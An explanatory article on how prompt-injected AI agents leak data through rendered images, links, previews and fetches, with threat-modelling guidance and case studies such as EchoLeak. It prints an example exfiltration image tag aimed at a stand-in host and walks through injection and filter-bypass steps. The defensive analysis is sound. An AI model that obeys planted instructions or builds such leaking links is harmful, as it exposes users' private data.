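# How Prompt-Injected AI Agents Leak Data Through Links and Visible Text

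## How outside text enters an agent and how data leaves it

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can call tools, for example to fetch web pages, search a mailbox, query a database or edit files. Strangers wrote much of the text it reads, and some of them hide instructions in a web page or an email. Security researchers call it indirect prompt injection when the model follows those instructions. A common aim is exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who is not entitled to it. An attacker can do this with a single web address that has the data written into it.

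### The agent loop and the context

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the loop that OpenAI's coding agent Codex runs, and other agents follow much the same pattern. The program around the model combines the operator's instructions, a description of each tool and the user's request into one long text, the prompt, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final answer or a request for a tool call, for instance to read a file. If it requests a tool call, the program runs it, appends the output to the prompt and sends the longer prompt back. This can go on for hundreds of calls before the model returns a final answer to the user.

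The context is all the text the model reads at one step. In Codex, each new prompt begins with an exact copy of the previous one. When the prompt passes a set length, the program replaces it with a shorter version. So a web page the agent fetched at step 3 is usually still in the context at step 40, along with anything the agent has since read from the user's files. The attacker's text can arrive before or after the secret, as long as both end up in the same context.

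### Why the model mixes up instructions and data

SQL injection is an older version of this problem, in which an attacker types a database command into a form field and the database runs it. Web developers prevent it with parameterised queries, which send the command and the typed-in value separately so that the database cannot run the value as a command. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models have no such separation. A model takes in one stream of tokens (words or pieces of words) and predicts the next token. In David C's example, a recruiter uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it. That line reaches the model in the same prompt as the recruiter's instructions. He thinks the flaw may never be completely fixed.

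Developers use tags to label text as coming from the system, the user or a tool, and train the model to rank some sources above others. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes such labels as useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary, and experiments on the internal workings of models suggest why.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) trained probes, small classifiers that read a model's internal activations, to detect which role tag surrounded a piece of text. They used identical web text under every tag so that the probes could learn only the effect of the tags. They then ran the probes on an ordinary conversation about gardening. Passages in the style of the model's private reasoning scored 85% as "reasoning" with the correct tags and 83% with no tags. The score was again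 85% when the researchers wrapped the whole conversation in user tags, so the style of the text had overridden its label.

In one test of data theft, an agent with access to a file of secrets had to summarise a web page containing hidden text. A fake user command worked 0 to 2% of the time on every model except gpt-oss-20b, where it worked 26% of the time. Adding text that imitated the model's own reasoning raised success to between 56 and 70%. Across 1,000 exfiltration attempts, success rose from 2% where the probes measured the least confusion about roles to 70% where they measured the most. The models were from OpenAI's gpt-oss, o4-mini and GPT-5 families, so the percentages are dated. Role confusion as the mechanism is harder to dismiss, because rewording the forged reasoning to remove its style but keep its argument cut success from 61% to 10%.

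Models resolve conflicting instructions inconsistently even without an attacker. Laddha, Pradhan and Srivastava (2026), in *Position, Role or Label?*, gave 14 open-weight models harmless conflicts, such as five different rules for capitalising field names, each from a different source. In one trial, Qwen3-8B ignored the operator and the user and followed the rule in a tool result. When an operator's rule came first in the system message, every Qwen model followed later lines instead in most conflicts, while gpt-oss mostly followed the operator's rule when it acted on any rule at all. The study did not test attacks or the big closed models. When two instructions clashed, at most 2.92% of the replies that followed one of them flagged or hedged the conflict, which is a concern for anyone relying on the model to warn them.

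Most prompt injection attempts against closed models fail. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts against 13 frontier models and succeeded 8,648 times, or about 3%. Every model failed at least once, with attack success rates ranging from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, both of which have newer successors. According to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), the security firm Gray Swan had held six rounds of its own contests of this kind by August 2026, with theft of private data among the goals.

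Email costs almost nothing to send, so an attacker with a 0.5% success rate can try many times. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance, the probability of at least one success in 200 attempts would be 1 − 0.995²⁰⁰, or about 63%. Real attempts are not independent, because a trick that fails once against a model tends to fail again, but real attackers also change their tricks.

### Links, images and web addresses

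The model's answer is text, and text on its own sends nothing anywhere. What happens next depends on the client, the program that displays the answer: a browser page, a chat app, an email reader, perhaps a log viewer. Many clients accept Markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting, and render it, meaning that they turn it into the headings, links and pictures the user sees. Addresses can appear in Markdown like this:

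```
A link:                  [returns policy](https://www.example.com/returns)
An image:                ![blue square](https://www.example.com/square.png)
A reference-style link:  [returns policy][r]

[r]: https://www.example.com/returns
```

A Markdown link shows the words in square brackets, and the browser normally contacts the server only if the user clicks. An image is written the same way with an exclamation mark in front, but a client that loads remote images fetches the image as soon as it displays the answer. Both can also be written in reference style, which puts the address under a label that can be much further down the text. A filter that searches only for round brackets directly after square ones will miss reference-style links and images.

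The address itself has several parts. Take `https://www.example.com/returns/form?order=70415#top`:

| Part | In this address | What becomes of it |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Tells the browser which protocol to use |
| Host | `www.example.com` | Determines which server gets the request |
| Path | `/returns/form` | Goes to the server |
| Query string | `order=70415` | Goes to the server |
| Fragment | `top` | Stays in the browser |

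Whoever writes a web address can put any text in its path or query string. The server receives the request even if it has no page at that address, and web servers normally log requests.

*Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, shows a line from a web server log. The line gives the time to the second, the path with its full query string, a status code, the size of the reply in bytes and a string identifying the browser, here Firefox 117 on a Mac. The query string contains the leaked data, a link to a video. Lines in this format start with the requester's network address, which Rehberger redacted. This is the user's own address when a browser loads an image directly, but when the agent requests a page with a fetch tool, it is the address of the machine the tool runs on.

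### One order number, step by step

Suppose Dana has an assistant that can read her email and fetch web pages. The order number below is invented, and the domain example.net is reserved for documentation, so no attacker can register it.

1. Dana asks whether she can still return her last order.
2. The assistant searches her mailbox and finds the confirmation of order 70415. The text of that email joins the context.
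3. The assistant fetches a web page about returns. Someone has left a comment at the bottom, aimed at AI assistants, that asks for a small picture at the end of the answer with the customer's order number in its address. The comment joins the context as well.
4. The model writes a perfectly good answer about returns and ends it with `![](https://pics.example.net/dot.png?order=70415)`.
5. Dana's client renders the answer. It converts the last line into an HTML image tag, and her browser requests the picture from pics.example.net. The picture is one transparent pixel, so she notices nothing.
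6. The server at pics.example.net adds a line to its log:

```
203.0.113.7 - - [05/Dec/2026:10:14:22 +0000] "GET /dot.png?order=70415 HTTP/1.1" 200 68 "-" "Mozilla/5.0 ..."
```

The owner of that server reads the order number in the log. An order number is of little use to a thief, but the same method would leak a password reset code.

### Two failures and three ingredients

Dana's order number leaked because the model followed instructions in an outsider's text and an outsider could see the result. The leak needed both. If the client had displayed the image line as plain text, the order number would have stayed on Dana's screen, even with the model fully under the attacker's influence. The client would also have had no image to load if the model had ignored the comment, however lax the client's rules for loading images were.

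Whether a model obeys a malicious instruction and whether an outsider can see the result are separate problems that call for different kinds of work. Nobody knows how to make a model ignore every malicious instruction, so work on the first problem can only make obedience less likely. The second depends mostly on ordinary software, which an engineer can inspect and change. David C therefore advises designers to put more effort into safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do, and less into keeping malicious text away from the model.

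Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, coined the popular term "lethal trifecta" for the dangerous combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. Removing any one of the three prevents this kind of theft. For example, an agent with no private data has none to leak, even if it follows an attacker's instructions. The trifecta is an excellent checklist, but many useful agents meet all three conditions, and it does not show how likely a leak is or how much data could get out.

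People also tend to read the third item too narrowly. Suppose Dana's assistant can only read her mail, and the attacker's instructions arrive in a message. The mailbox supplies both the private data and the untrusted content. The assistant has no tool that sends anything, but her order number still leaks because the client loads the picture. An audit that lists only the agent's tools would pass this system as safe.

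### Where the attack came from

Leaks through remotely loaded content are older than chatbots. In *Efail*, Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues (2018) used them to read encrypted email. In the simplest variant, the attacker already has an encrypted message and mails it back to the victim between two pieces of HTML, one that opens an image address and one that closes it. A vulnerable mail client decrypts the message, joins the parts into a single page and requests an image whose address contains the decrypted text. The attack works without a language model because the client itself incorrectly joins trusted and untrusted text.

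Until then, as Poddebniak and colleagues pointed out, people had treated remote loading in email only as a privacy threat, because it let the sender learn whether, when and from which network address someone had opened a message. With this method and a more elaborate one that altered the encrypted text, they found ways to get data out of 23 of 35 clients for S/MIME and 10 of 28 for OpenPGP, the two main standards for encrypted mail. Vendors issued fixes, but according to the researchers' EFAIL website, bypasses for Thunderbird and Apple Mail followed.

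The Markdown version appeared in spring 2023. In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Samoilenko described a website that secretly adds instructions to any text a visitor copies from it. When the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, the answers include an invisible image whose address contains parts of the chat. Willison (2023) drew attention to the report on 14 April. Samoilenko acknowledged that the attack was unreliable, with results varying from run to run, and found it easy to extract earlier prompts or code but very difficult to extract passwords.

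Rehberger found the same leak independently a few days after Samoilenko, and his versions did not require the user to paste anything. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, he had ChatGPT read the attacker's page through a browsing plugin. In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, he explained that a comment or an advertisement on the page the user was viewing was enough to cause the leak in Microsoft's Bing Chat. In that demonstration, the image appeared a couple of exchanges after the model had read the malicious text, when the user might well have forgotten the page.

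Rehberger reported the problem to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI the next day. Microsoft fixed it with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule that limits the domains from which a browser may load a web page's images. His later Embrace The Red post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the fix to May 2023, while his original post says Microsoft told him about it on 15 June. OpenAI replied that rendering images was a feature and that it planned no change, but it began checking image addresses in December.

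*Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) lists eleven products in which Rehberger had found the image leak by the end of 2024, including Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. Vendors promptly fixed almost all the exfiltration attacks that Willison had collected by mid-2025, usually by blocking the route the data took out, which left the models as vulnerable to prompt injection as before.

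## Working out what the attacker can observe

A vendor can block only the routes it knows about. Anyone securing an agent or judging its security therefore needs a threat model, which is a written statement of who the attacker is, what they can do and what they can see. For data theft, the hardest part is working out what the attacker can see, because agents have many effects that people don't usually think of as sending data.

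In an invented example, a small firm sells routers, and its support agent reads tickets that anyone can submit through a web form. The agent can fetch web pages, such as a manual or a page that a customer links to, and it posts bug reports on a public tracker. Its instructions contain the six-digit code for the firm's courier account. When the firm owes a customer a free return, the agent includes the code in its summary for a member of staff, who books the parcel and writes back to the customer. A stranger with the code could send parcels at the firm's expense.

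### Listing the effects

1. List every outward effect, meaning anything the agent's work changes outside the agent: a network request, a message, a comment, a download counter. The list of tools gives only some of them. Add whatever the client loads when it displays an answer, and whatever other services do with the agent's posts, such as sending notification emails or fetching link previews. Recording the network traffic of a few ordinary jobs usually turns up something missing from the diagram.
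2. Name who sees each effect. Use roles rather than people, because one attacker can hold several roles.
3. State exactly what each observer sees, field by field. "The server sees the request" is too vague to check. "The time to the second, the path, the query string and the requester's network address" is something an engineer can compare with a log.
4. For each secret, ask whether a different value could change any of those fields.

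Even reading a web page can send data out. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) describes a command shell for agents that tracks which private or untrusted data a command has touched. The shell treats every network request as an outward effect, even a plain request for a page, because the server can store what the address contains. The paper mentions OpenAI agents that had permission only to read the web but still wrote to a public wiki. A web search can also have visible effects. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a search that changes a site's visitor statistics.

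### Who sees what

The owner of a requested server gets a log line like the one that gave away Dana's order number. Blocking the request may not prevent the leak, because the computer first looks up the server's name, and that lookup can go to a name server that the domain's owner runs. A lookup of `70415.example.net` can deliver an order number even if a firewall then stops the page request.

Permitted third-party services are harder to reason about. An allow-list often names a whole service, such as a code-hosting site or a cloud store, where an attacker can open an account. The attacker cannot read the service's logs, but can see what the service shows its customers, such as download counts, page visits and data sent with a particular access key. If the agent's request carries the attacker's key, the data ends up in the attacker's account, even though the address is on the allow-list.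 Kim and colleagues give one label to everything that comes from a host, so their system does not distinguish a firm's own GitHub project from an attacker's.

The provider of a tool receives every argument in full. If the router firm rents its fetch tool from another company, that company gets the whole address, including the fragment, which a browser would not send, even if the page does not exist. The company that hosts the model receives the most, because it gets the entire context. Firms normally have contracts with such providers, but anyone can publish a tool. A malicious provider can also choose its answer after reading the arguments, and so steer the agent's next step. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) proves security results for a range of agent designs but excludes tools of this sort.

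Readers of shared text, such as comments on a public tracker, see the wording, author, time, labels and often the edit history. Subscribers may have received the first version by email, so deleting a comment a minute later does not undo the leak.

A person who talks to the agent sees its replies, refusals, error messages and delays, and in some products its tool calls. This matters little if all the data belong to that person, but a great deal if one assistant serves many customers from a shared data store. In one of Dongol's cases, planted text makes the agent call an internal tool that a private setting either permits or forbids. The agent sends nothing outside the system, but an error message naming the refused tool reveals the setting.

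The last observer is someone watching the network, such as the operator of a hotel's Wi-Fi. Encryption hides paths, query strings and page contents, but usually leaves the server's name and the size and time of each transfer visible. Costa and colleagues exclude timing and packet length from their model. That is reasonable for an agent in a data centre whose attackers are strangers on the web, but an agent on a journalist's laptop needs a model that covers both.

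An attacker with a web server and a tracker account sees both the requests sent to the server and the text visible on the tracker. The analysis should combine the two views, because the attacker can join half a code from each into the whole code.

### What counts as a leak

A run is the complete record of one job, including the user's request, everything the agent read, every model output, every tool call and all timestamps. For each observer, an observation function O takes a run and returns exactly what that observer sees of it. For the owner of a web server, O returns the list of log lines the run produced. If the run produced none, O returns an empty list, which also counts as an observation.

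Noninterference goes back to Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*. SRI, the research institute where the theory originated, explains that one party is noninterfering with another if nothing it does can influence what the other later sees. For an agent, write run(s, a) for the run with secret s and attacker's text a, keeping everything else fixed. Noninterference then requires

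```
O(run(s, a)) = O(run(s′, a))
```

for every text a and every pair of secrets s and s′. A leak is a counterexample: one attacker's text, two secrets and two different observations.

Noninterference can fail even when no secret data appears in any address. Suppose an attacker has put a file on a storage site that the router firm's allow-list permits. A ticket causes the agent to fetch that file if the first digit of the courier code is even, and to fetch nothing otherwise. The address is the same every time and contains nothing private. The file's download counter goes up by one if the code is 482913 but doesn't change if it is 582913. The attacker's observations differ between the two codes, so noninterference fails and the attacker learns whether the first digit is even.

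A filter that searches addresses for the code would find nothing here. Some formal definitions don't cover this leak either. Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy, which covers private data that flow into an action but not what an outsider can infer from the choice of action. It is weaker than full noninterference, which they consider too restrictive for a useful agent because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible tool call after the agent has read something private.

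Dongol's basic attacker sees the content and order of messages, but the definition compares two runs only if the same number of messages reach the attacker between consecutive reads. It therefore never compares a run with one request to a run with none, and misses the leak when the secret determines which of the two occurs. Dongol gives a very similar example in which planted text makes the agent request either a permitted newsletter or a forbidden address, depending on the secret. A second attacker, who also sees when each step happens, does detect the leak. Anyone writing their own observation function can avoid the problem by comparing all pairs of runs in which the attacker's text is the same, however many requests each run contains.

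Whether an agent is secure can depend on whether the attacker can observe timing, so the question has no answer until O is specified. In another of Dongol's cases, the user approves the exact text of each outgoing reply. Planted text makes the agent try to send a private value instead, and the runtime monitor, the program that checks each call, allows this only if the value equals the approved reply. The recipient gets a single message with the approved text either way, but it leaves one step earlier if the private value matches. Someone who sees only content learns nothing, while someone who can time the message learns whether the two are equal.

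Language models also vary from run to run, so two runs can differ even with the same secret. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) therefore compares probabilities, requiring that for any two secrets, the distributions of everything that leaves the agent differ by at most a small amount δ. The paper uses this as a standard for comparison and does not claim that its system meets it. Suppose the storage site's counter goes up in 40% of runs when the secret's first digit is even and in 30% when it is odd. Then δ is at least 0.1, and an attacker who sees one run can correctly guess whether the digit is even or odd 55% of the time instead of 50%. Nobody can detect such a leak from a single log, because the definition compares probabilities across runs.

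An agent sometimes has to disclose private information to do its job. Dongol describes a calendar assistant that tells anyone who requests a meeting when its user is free, which strict noninterference forbids. Dongol instead compares the agent with an imaginary twin that does the same task but never obeys planted text, and counts as leaks only the disclosures that the twin could not produce under any input. By this standard, planted text may cause the assistant to send the calendar, since a genuine request would have obtained it too, but it causes a leak if it makes the assistant add a password reset code.

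Dongol also points out a loophole in this comparison. Suppose an agent's task is to tell callers whether the code they give is correct. Each guess reveals very little, but for any two codes, some guess would tell them apart. Under the basic definition, planted text that extracts the whole code therefore adds no leak. Dongol's stricter definition closes this loophole. A threat model should state how much the task may reveal per run, as well as what it may reveal.

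The router firm can mostly avoid the difficulty by treating each secret separately. A bug report has to depend on the customer's ticket but should never depend on the courier code. Plain noninterference is therefore a sensible requirement for the code and for every observer except the staff.

### Data used and data recovered

An agent may read a private record without anyone outside learning its contents. *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (Huang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) separates internal exposure, the private items that the system selects and works with, from external leakage, the items that an attacker can recover from what they see. Its framework, CIPL, follows data through selection, assembly into the context, execution and observation. In attempt j, U<sub>j</sub> is the set of private items the system selects and V<sub>j</sub> is the set the attacker recovers. The attacker's total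 after n attempts is the number of distinct items across V<sub>1</sub> to V<sub>n</sub>.

If the support agent reads a customer's name, address and router model while handling a ticket, but mentions only the model in its bug report, all three items are in U and only the model is in V. An incident report based on what the agent read would count three leaked items instead of one. Searching the public text for exact copies can understate the loss. Alpay and Alpay (2026), in *AgentSecBench*, point out that finding a canary (a made-up secret placed in a test) proves a leak, but failing to find one does not rule out a leak, since the model may have paraphrased it.

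CIPL counts recovered items, such as records or fields. This is useful after an incident, when someone has to say which records got out. It is less suitable for designing a system, because the download counter above would score zero. Comparing complete observations avoids this problem. Li and colleagues note that the comparison covers raw bytes, so encoded, paraphrased or split-up secrets need no separate rule.

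### What to assume about the attacker

A good starting assumption is that the attacker knows the agent's configuration, including its instructions, tools, model and filters. Kim and colleagues assume this. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) instead assumes an attacker who can publish web pages and send emails but has no access to the agent's instructions, which probably describes most attackers. But anyone can send the router firm harmless tickets and study the bug reports that come out, and if a vendor sells one agent to a thousand firms, any of them could study it to plan an attack. Assuming the attacker knows the configuration also loses little, since it rules out only defences that depend on the attacker's ignorance. The one exception here is the courier code, which is in the instructions but which we assume the attacker doesn't know.

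An attacker who knows the configuration can't necessarily change it. Li and colleagues assume the attacker can write tool descriptions and skills (reusable instructions that users install). A firm that installs either from strangers needs to assume the same.

This analysis assumes that the attacker cannot read the model's inputs and outputs directly, because an attacker who could would already have the code and would not need prompt injection. Somebody has to check that assumption against the deployment. It is false if the agent writes its transcript to a public build log, or if staff share conversations through links that anyone can open. A transcript exposed in either way is an outward effect and needs its own line in the list.

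Repeated attempts are harder to rule out, because a ticket costs nothing and *AttriGuard* (2026) allows the attacker to plant text in tool results at any step of a job and across several steps. Li and colleagues also let the attacker adapt to the outcome of each defence. The courier code stays the same from ticket to ticket, so the attacker can combine small leaks. With the 40% and 30% rates above, an attacker who counts downloads over a hundred independent runs can tell an even first digit from an odd one about 85% of the time. Limits on tickets per person help only if the attacker cannot easily pose as many people. Changing the code every week would help more, since digits from old codes would no longer be useful.

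The attacker doesn't need to reply to the agent's request, because the request itself delivers the data. Inspecting the response is therefore too late, so Kim and colleagues check network requests before sending them, whereas they can hold back file changes until a command has finished. An attacker who does reply is more dangerous, because each reply can contain new instructions based on what the last request revealed.

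Finally, the attacker may be able to show agents something people do not see. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) describes pages that look credible to a human reader but carry instructions in their metadata, such as the description a site supplies for link previews. A server can also send the agent a different page altogether, because it receives the requester's network address and browser string before it responds. An employee who opens a suspicious link in a browser and finds an ordinary manual therefore learns little about what the agent received. To investigate, the firm needs a copy of the exact text that entered the agent's context.

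### Three published threat models

Three papers from 2026 set out quite different attackers. None is a safe template to copy without changes.

| | Lan and colleagues, February | Huang and colleagues, March | Kim and colleagues, November |
|---|---|---|---|
| How the attacker gets text in | Public web pages, metadata and redirects | Messages to the agent | Data that tools return, such as web pages and emails |
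| What the attacker knows | Nothing about the configuration | The application and type of task, and perhaps hints about how it selects data | The whole configuration |
| What the attacker sees | Requests to their own server | Whatever the product exposes: answers, cited evidence, tool arguments or tool results | Certain effects of tool calls and shell commands |
| What is missing | Name lookups and timing, which the experiments did not test | Text planted by third parties | Malicious tool descriptions |

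Lan and colleagues deliberately made the attack easier by placing the secret directly in the context, keeping the system instructions minimal and spelling out the format for tool calls. This setup exaggerates the danger for a product that loads a secret only when a task needs it, but it fits the router firm, whose agent always has the code in its context. In other respects, their attacker is weaker than the one the firm faces. They rule out an attacker who inserts messages into the conversation, but anyone can write a ticket. They also record only what reaches the attacker's own collection server, so their measurements would miss a leak through the public tracker.

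Huang and colleagues assume that the attacker is the person using the agent. This threat model suits a shop's assistant that answers thousands of customers from one store of past conversations, where any customer might try to steal the others' data. They also allow the attacker a set number of queries, which is more realistic than a single attempt. The model doesn't suit a personal email assistant, because the user owns the mailbox and the attacker is someone who sends mail to it. It can also overstate what the attacker sees, since some of their experiments expose tool arguments or tool results, and a customer filling in a web form normally sees neither.

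For an agent that reads outsiders' text and uses tools, Kim and colleagues provide the best starting point of the three. Their attack tests gave the attacker full control over the model's output as soon as the model received planted text. This assumption would greatly overestimate how often theft will happen, but it is the right one for testing a barrier that should hold whatever the model does.

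Their model still needs some additions. They trust tool descriptions, which is risky for a product with a marketplace of third-party tools. They also treat the agent's instructions as known to the attacker, so a firm that copied the model without thinking might label the courier code public. The effects they list come from tool calls and shell commands, and leave out images that a client loads when it displays an answer. Costa and colleagues, whose policies the model builds on, also treat answers to the user as harmless by default, though they say designers can check answers too. Dongol states explicitly that this holds only if showing a reply has no effect the attacker can see, such as loading an image. Li and colleagues count the answer as one of the places where data can leave, which is the safer choice for any agent with a graphical client.

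### The support agent's table

The router firm's agent fetches pages through a rented service and may fetch them from any address. Staff read its summaries in a web console. The last column shows how the courier code could affect what the observer sees, assuming that planted text fully controls the model.

| Outward effect | Who sees it | Exactly what they see | How the code could show |
|---|---|---|---|
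| Fetch from the attacker's site | Owner of the requested server | Time, path, query string, headers and the fetch service's network address, or no request at all | Digits in the address, choice of page, request or silence |
| Fetch from a public storage site | Account holder at that site | Download count of their own file, and anything that arrives under their access key | A change in the count, or digits sent with the key |
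| Any fetch | Provider of the fetch tool | The complete address and the time, even if the fetch fails | Digits anywhere in the address, including the fragment |
| Bug report | Readers of the tracker and email subscribers | Title, text, labels, time and edits, or no report | Digits in plain or disguised form, choice of label, report or silence |
| Summary in the console | Member of staff who works with the agent | The full text | By design, since staff need the code |
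| Image that the console loads from a summary | Owner of the requested server | The same fields as for a fetch, but with the employee's network address | Digits in the image's address |
| Answer to the ticket | Customer | What the member of staff writes, and when | Only if the member of staff passes it on |
| Connections from the firm's office | Network observer there | Names of the fetch service and of any image servers, with sizes and times | Digits in an image server's name, or the number and size of transfers |

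The person who talks to this agent is an employee who is allowed to see the code, so that row needs no separate defence. That would change if the firm let the agent answer customers directly, because the ticket's author would then see its wording, refusals and delays, and could follow up on each of them.

The rented fetch service hides the names of fetched sites from someone watching the office network, who sees only connections to the service. But it also lets another company, the service's operator, see every address. This is a good exchange if the firm has more reason to distrust someone watching its network than the operator.

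An allow-list on the fetch tool would block the attacker's own site but leave the storage site open if staff needed it. It would not affect the tracker, where the agent must be able to publish text influenced by a stranger's ticket. It would also not affect the image row, because the employee's browser makes that request. Whether that row is a real danger depends on how the console treats an image address in the agent's text, which the firm can check without studying the model.

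## Checking what the client loads when it displays an answer

The router firm can find out in a few minutes whether its console loads images. An engineer writes a test summary by hand, includes an image hosted on a server the firm controls, opens the summary in the console and checks the server's log. If the log shows a request for the image, the console loaded it, and anything the agent writes into a summary can leave the firm. The test doesn't use the model, so the result doesn't depend on what the model writes.

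As with Dana's order number, the browser requests the image when it displays the text. By then the agent has finished, and its tool log looks normal because it called no tool. The only records of the leak are the browser's network traffic, the log of any proxy on the firm's network, and the log of the server that received the data.

Images are the usual route, but browsers also load stylesheets, fonts, videos and embedded pages without a click. Markdown has no syntax for these, though many Markdown renderers accept raw HTML, which lets the model include any of them.

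### Images, links, previews and diagrams

Security researchers call a leak "zero-click" if the victim only has to use the product normally, and "one-click" if the victim has to follow a link. The table compares the common cases. In each, the server's owner gets the URL's path and query string, including any secret the model put there.

| What the text contains | When the request goes out | Who makes it | What else the server's owner learns |
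|---|---|---|---|
| Image, loaded directly | When the client displays the answer | The user's browser or app | The user's network address and browser, and when they read the answer |
| Image, loaded through a proxy | When the client displays the answer | The vendor's server | Roughly when the user read the answer |
| Link | When the user clicks | The user's browser | The same as for a direct image, plus whatever the user does on the page that opens |
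| Link in a messaging app with previews | When the agent posts the message | Usually the messaging platform's server | Which platform it is, and when the agent posted |
| Diagram with a picture in it | When the client draws the diagram | The user's browser, or a server that draws diagrams | The same as for an image that the same party requests |

When a message containing a link arrives, the platform fetches the linked page to build a preview. This hides the user's network address but still leaks any data in the web address, such as a password. The fetch happens earlier than an image request would, so the data leaks even if the user never reads the message.

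Diagrams are easy to overlook. Some clients draw them from text that the model writes in a notation such as Mermaid. If the renderer allows images inside the diagram, the browser requests them like any other images. A filter that searches for Markdown images misses these URLs because they are inside what looks like a code block. Other clients send the text to a separate drawing service. The operator of that service receives every word in the diagram, even if it contains no images, and belongs in the threat model.

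The user may not see any sign of a leak. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* shows Microsoft's Copilot Chat leaking a developer's API key (a password for software) through an image address. The researchers had already cancelled the key. No picture appeared in the chat, but the request still reached their server.

### Every place that displays the text

A firm that blocks images in its chat window has secured only that client. The same answer may later appear in a Slack channel, a notification email or a log, and each of those has its own rules about what to load.

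*Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, a 2026 post by PromptArmor, which tests AI products for security flaws, covers agents that people talk to through Slack or Telegram. Planted text makes the agent reply with a link that has private data in its address, and the data leaks when the app requests the link to show a preview. OpenClaw, an agent that people run themselves and often message from their phones, leaked data this way with its default Telegram settings.

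One line in OpenClaw's configuration file turns off Telegram link previews. The drawback is small, since links only lose their title and thumbnail. But the agent's developer can use such a setting only if the messaging app offers one, and the app's developer can't know which messages come from an agent that reads strangers' text. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to let developers turn previews off for individual channels.

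People who investigate attacks also need a safe client. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes an attack on a mock banking tool that checked customers' identities using six sources, one of which contained planted text from the web. The model's answer included a Markdown image with the customer's details in its address. A second model, which reviewed the answers, flagged this one and blocked it from being displayed in the tool. When a developer later opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, the viewer rendered the image, and the developer's browser sent the details to the attacker.

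The leak would have been the same if the banking tool had shown only plain text. Removing the image may even draw a reviewer's attention to the answer. PromptArmor shows a reply from the AI search engine Perplexity that was strangely empty because software had removed an image. A user might well give such a reply a thumbs-down, and a developer might then open it in the log. The attacker would also learn when someone started looking into the incident.

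PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed the report as not applicable on 4 December. OpenAI learned of the flaw only from the published article. It confirmed the flaw and reopened the report on 22 January 2026, saying a fix was under way. PromptArmor's timeline ends there. Anyone who reviews agent conversations in that viewer should test it with a harmless image first. Developers should do the same with the windows where they preview unfinished agents, because PromptArmor found the same problem in several of OpenAI's.

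An agent can also send the leaking text to another client. Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that works across a user's mail, chats and files. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks for permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting in Teams, Microsoft's chat app. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, which Willison discussed on 26 May 2026, reports that messages to the user's own account go out without approval and that users can't change this.

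The exception is risky even though users may see their own data. The messages can contain images from outside servers, which Teams or Outlook loads when the user opens the message. In PromptArmor's test, the planted text was in a skill file that the user had uploaded. It made Cowork collect download links that work for anyone who has them and put those links into image addresses. When the user opened the message, the attacker received the links and could use those few hundred characters to download whole documents.

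The attack used five lines planted in an 81-line file and worked in all five trials. Five trials are too few to give a precise success rate, but they prove that data can leak this way. The user had little chance of noticing, because Cowork's record of the task never displayed the contents of the message. PromptArmor presents the problem as a risk in the product's design and reports no fix. Administrators can block downloads of SharePoint files, but users can then open those files only in a browser, without printing, syncing or editing them in Word. That is a serious restriction, and attackers can still use the image route to leak anything short enough to fit into an address, such as a password.

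### Removing images and links

The simplest defence is to remove anything the client could load. A program between the model and the screen, called a sanitiser, deletes images or turns them into plain text, and may do the same with links. Users then lose charts and product photos. Losing links is worse, because people need them to check an assistant's sources.

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches an employee's mail, files and chats, had a filter of this kind, and the attack known as EchoLeak got past it. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains how his team at Aim Labs did it:

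1. The attacker emailed an employee. Microsoft's detector for planted instructions missed the email because its wording addressed the human recipient and never mentioned AI.
2. The email repeated its instructions under many headings about ordinary office topics, such as leave and onboarding. Copilot's search was then likely to retrieve some part of it whatever the employee asked about.
3. When that happened, the email entered the context along with internal data. The model followed the instructions and put the most sensitive item into an image address.
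4. Microsoft's filter removed outside links and images written in the ordinary way, but did not recognise reference-style ones. The image survived.
5. The browser still had a rule about where images could come from. The researchers got round it with an address belonging to Microsoft Teams.

The filter failed because it didn't recognize every notation that the client renders as an image. Adding a pattern for reference-style images would fix this case, but another unusual notation could still get through. A sounder design runs the same parser as the client, checks the resulting elements, and drops any image that isn't expressly permitted, however the model wrote it.

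Aim Labs reported EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) in January 2025 and Microsoft finished patching it that May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Microsoft says that nobody exploited the flaw and that customers need to do nothing, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. *EchoLeak* (2025), an academic case study, calls it the first known case of prompt injection causing concrete data theft in a production AI system. That overstates its novelty, given the leaks from ChatGPT and Bing Chat in 2023. Ravia makes the narrower claim that the victim did not have to point the assistant at a malicious page and that the attacker could take anything in the assistant's context.

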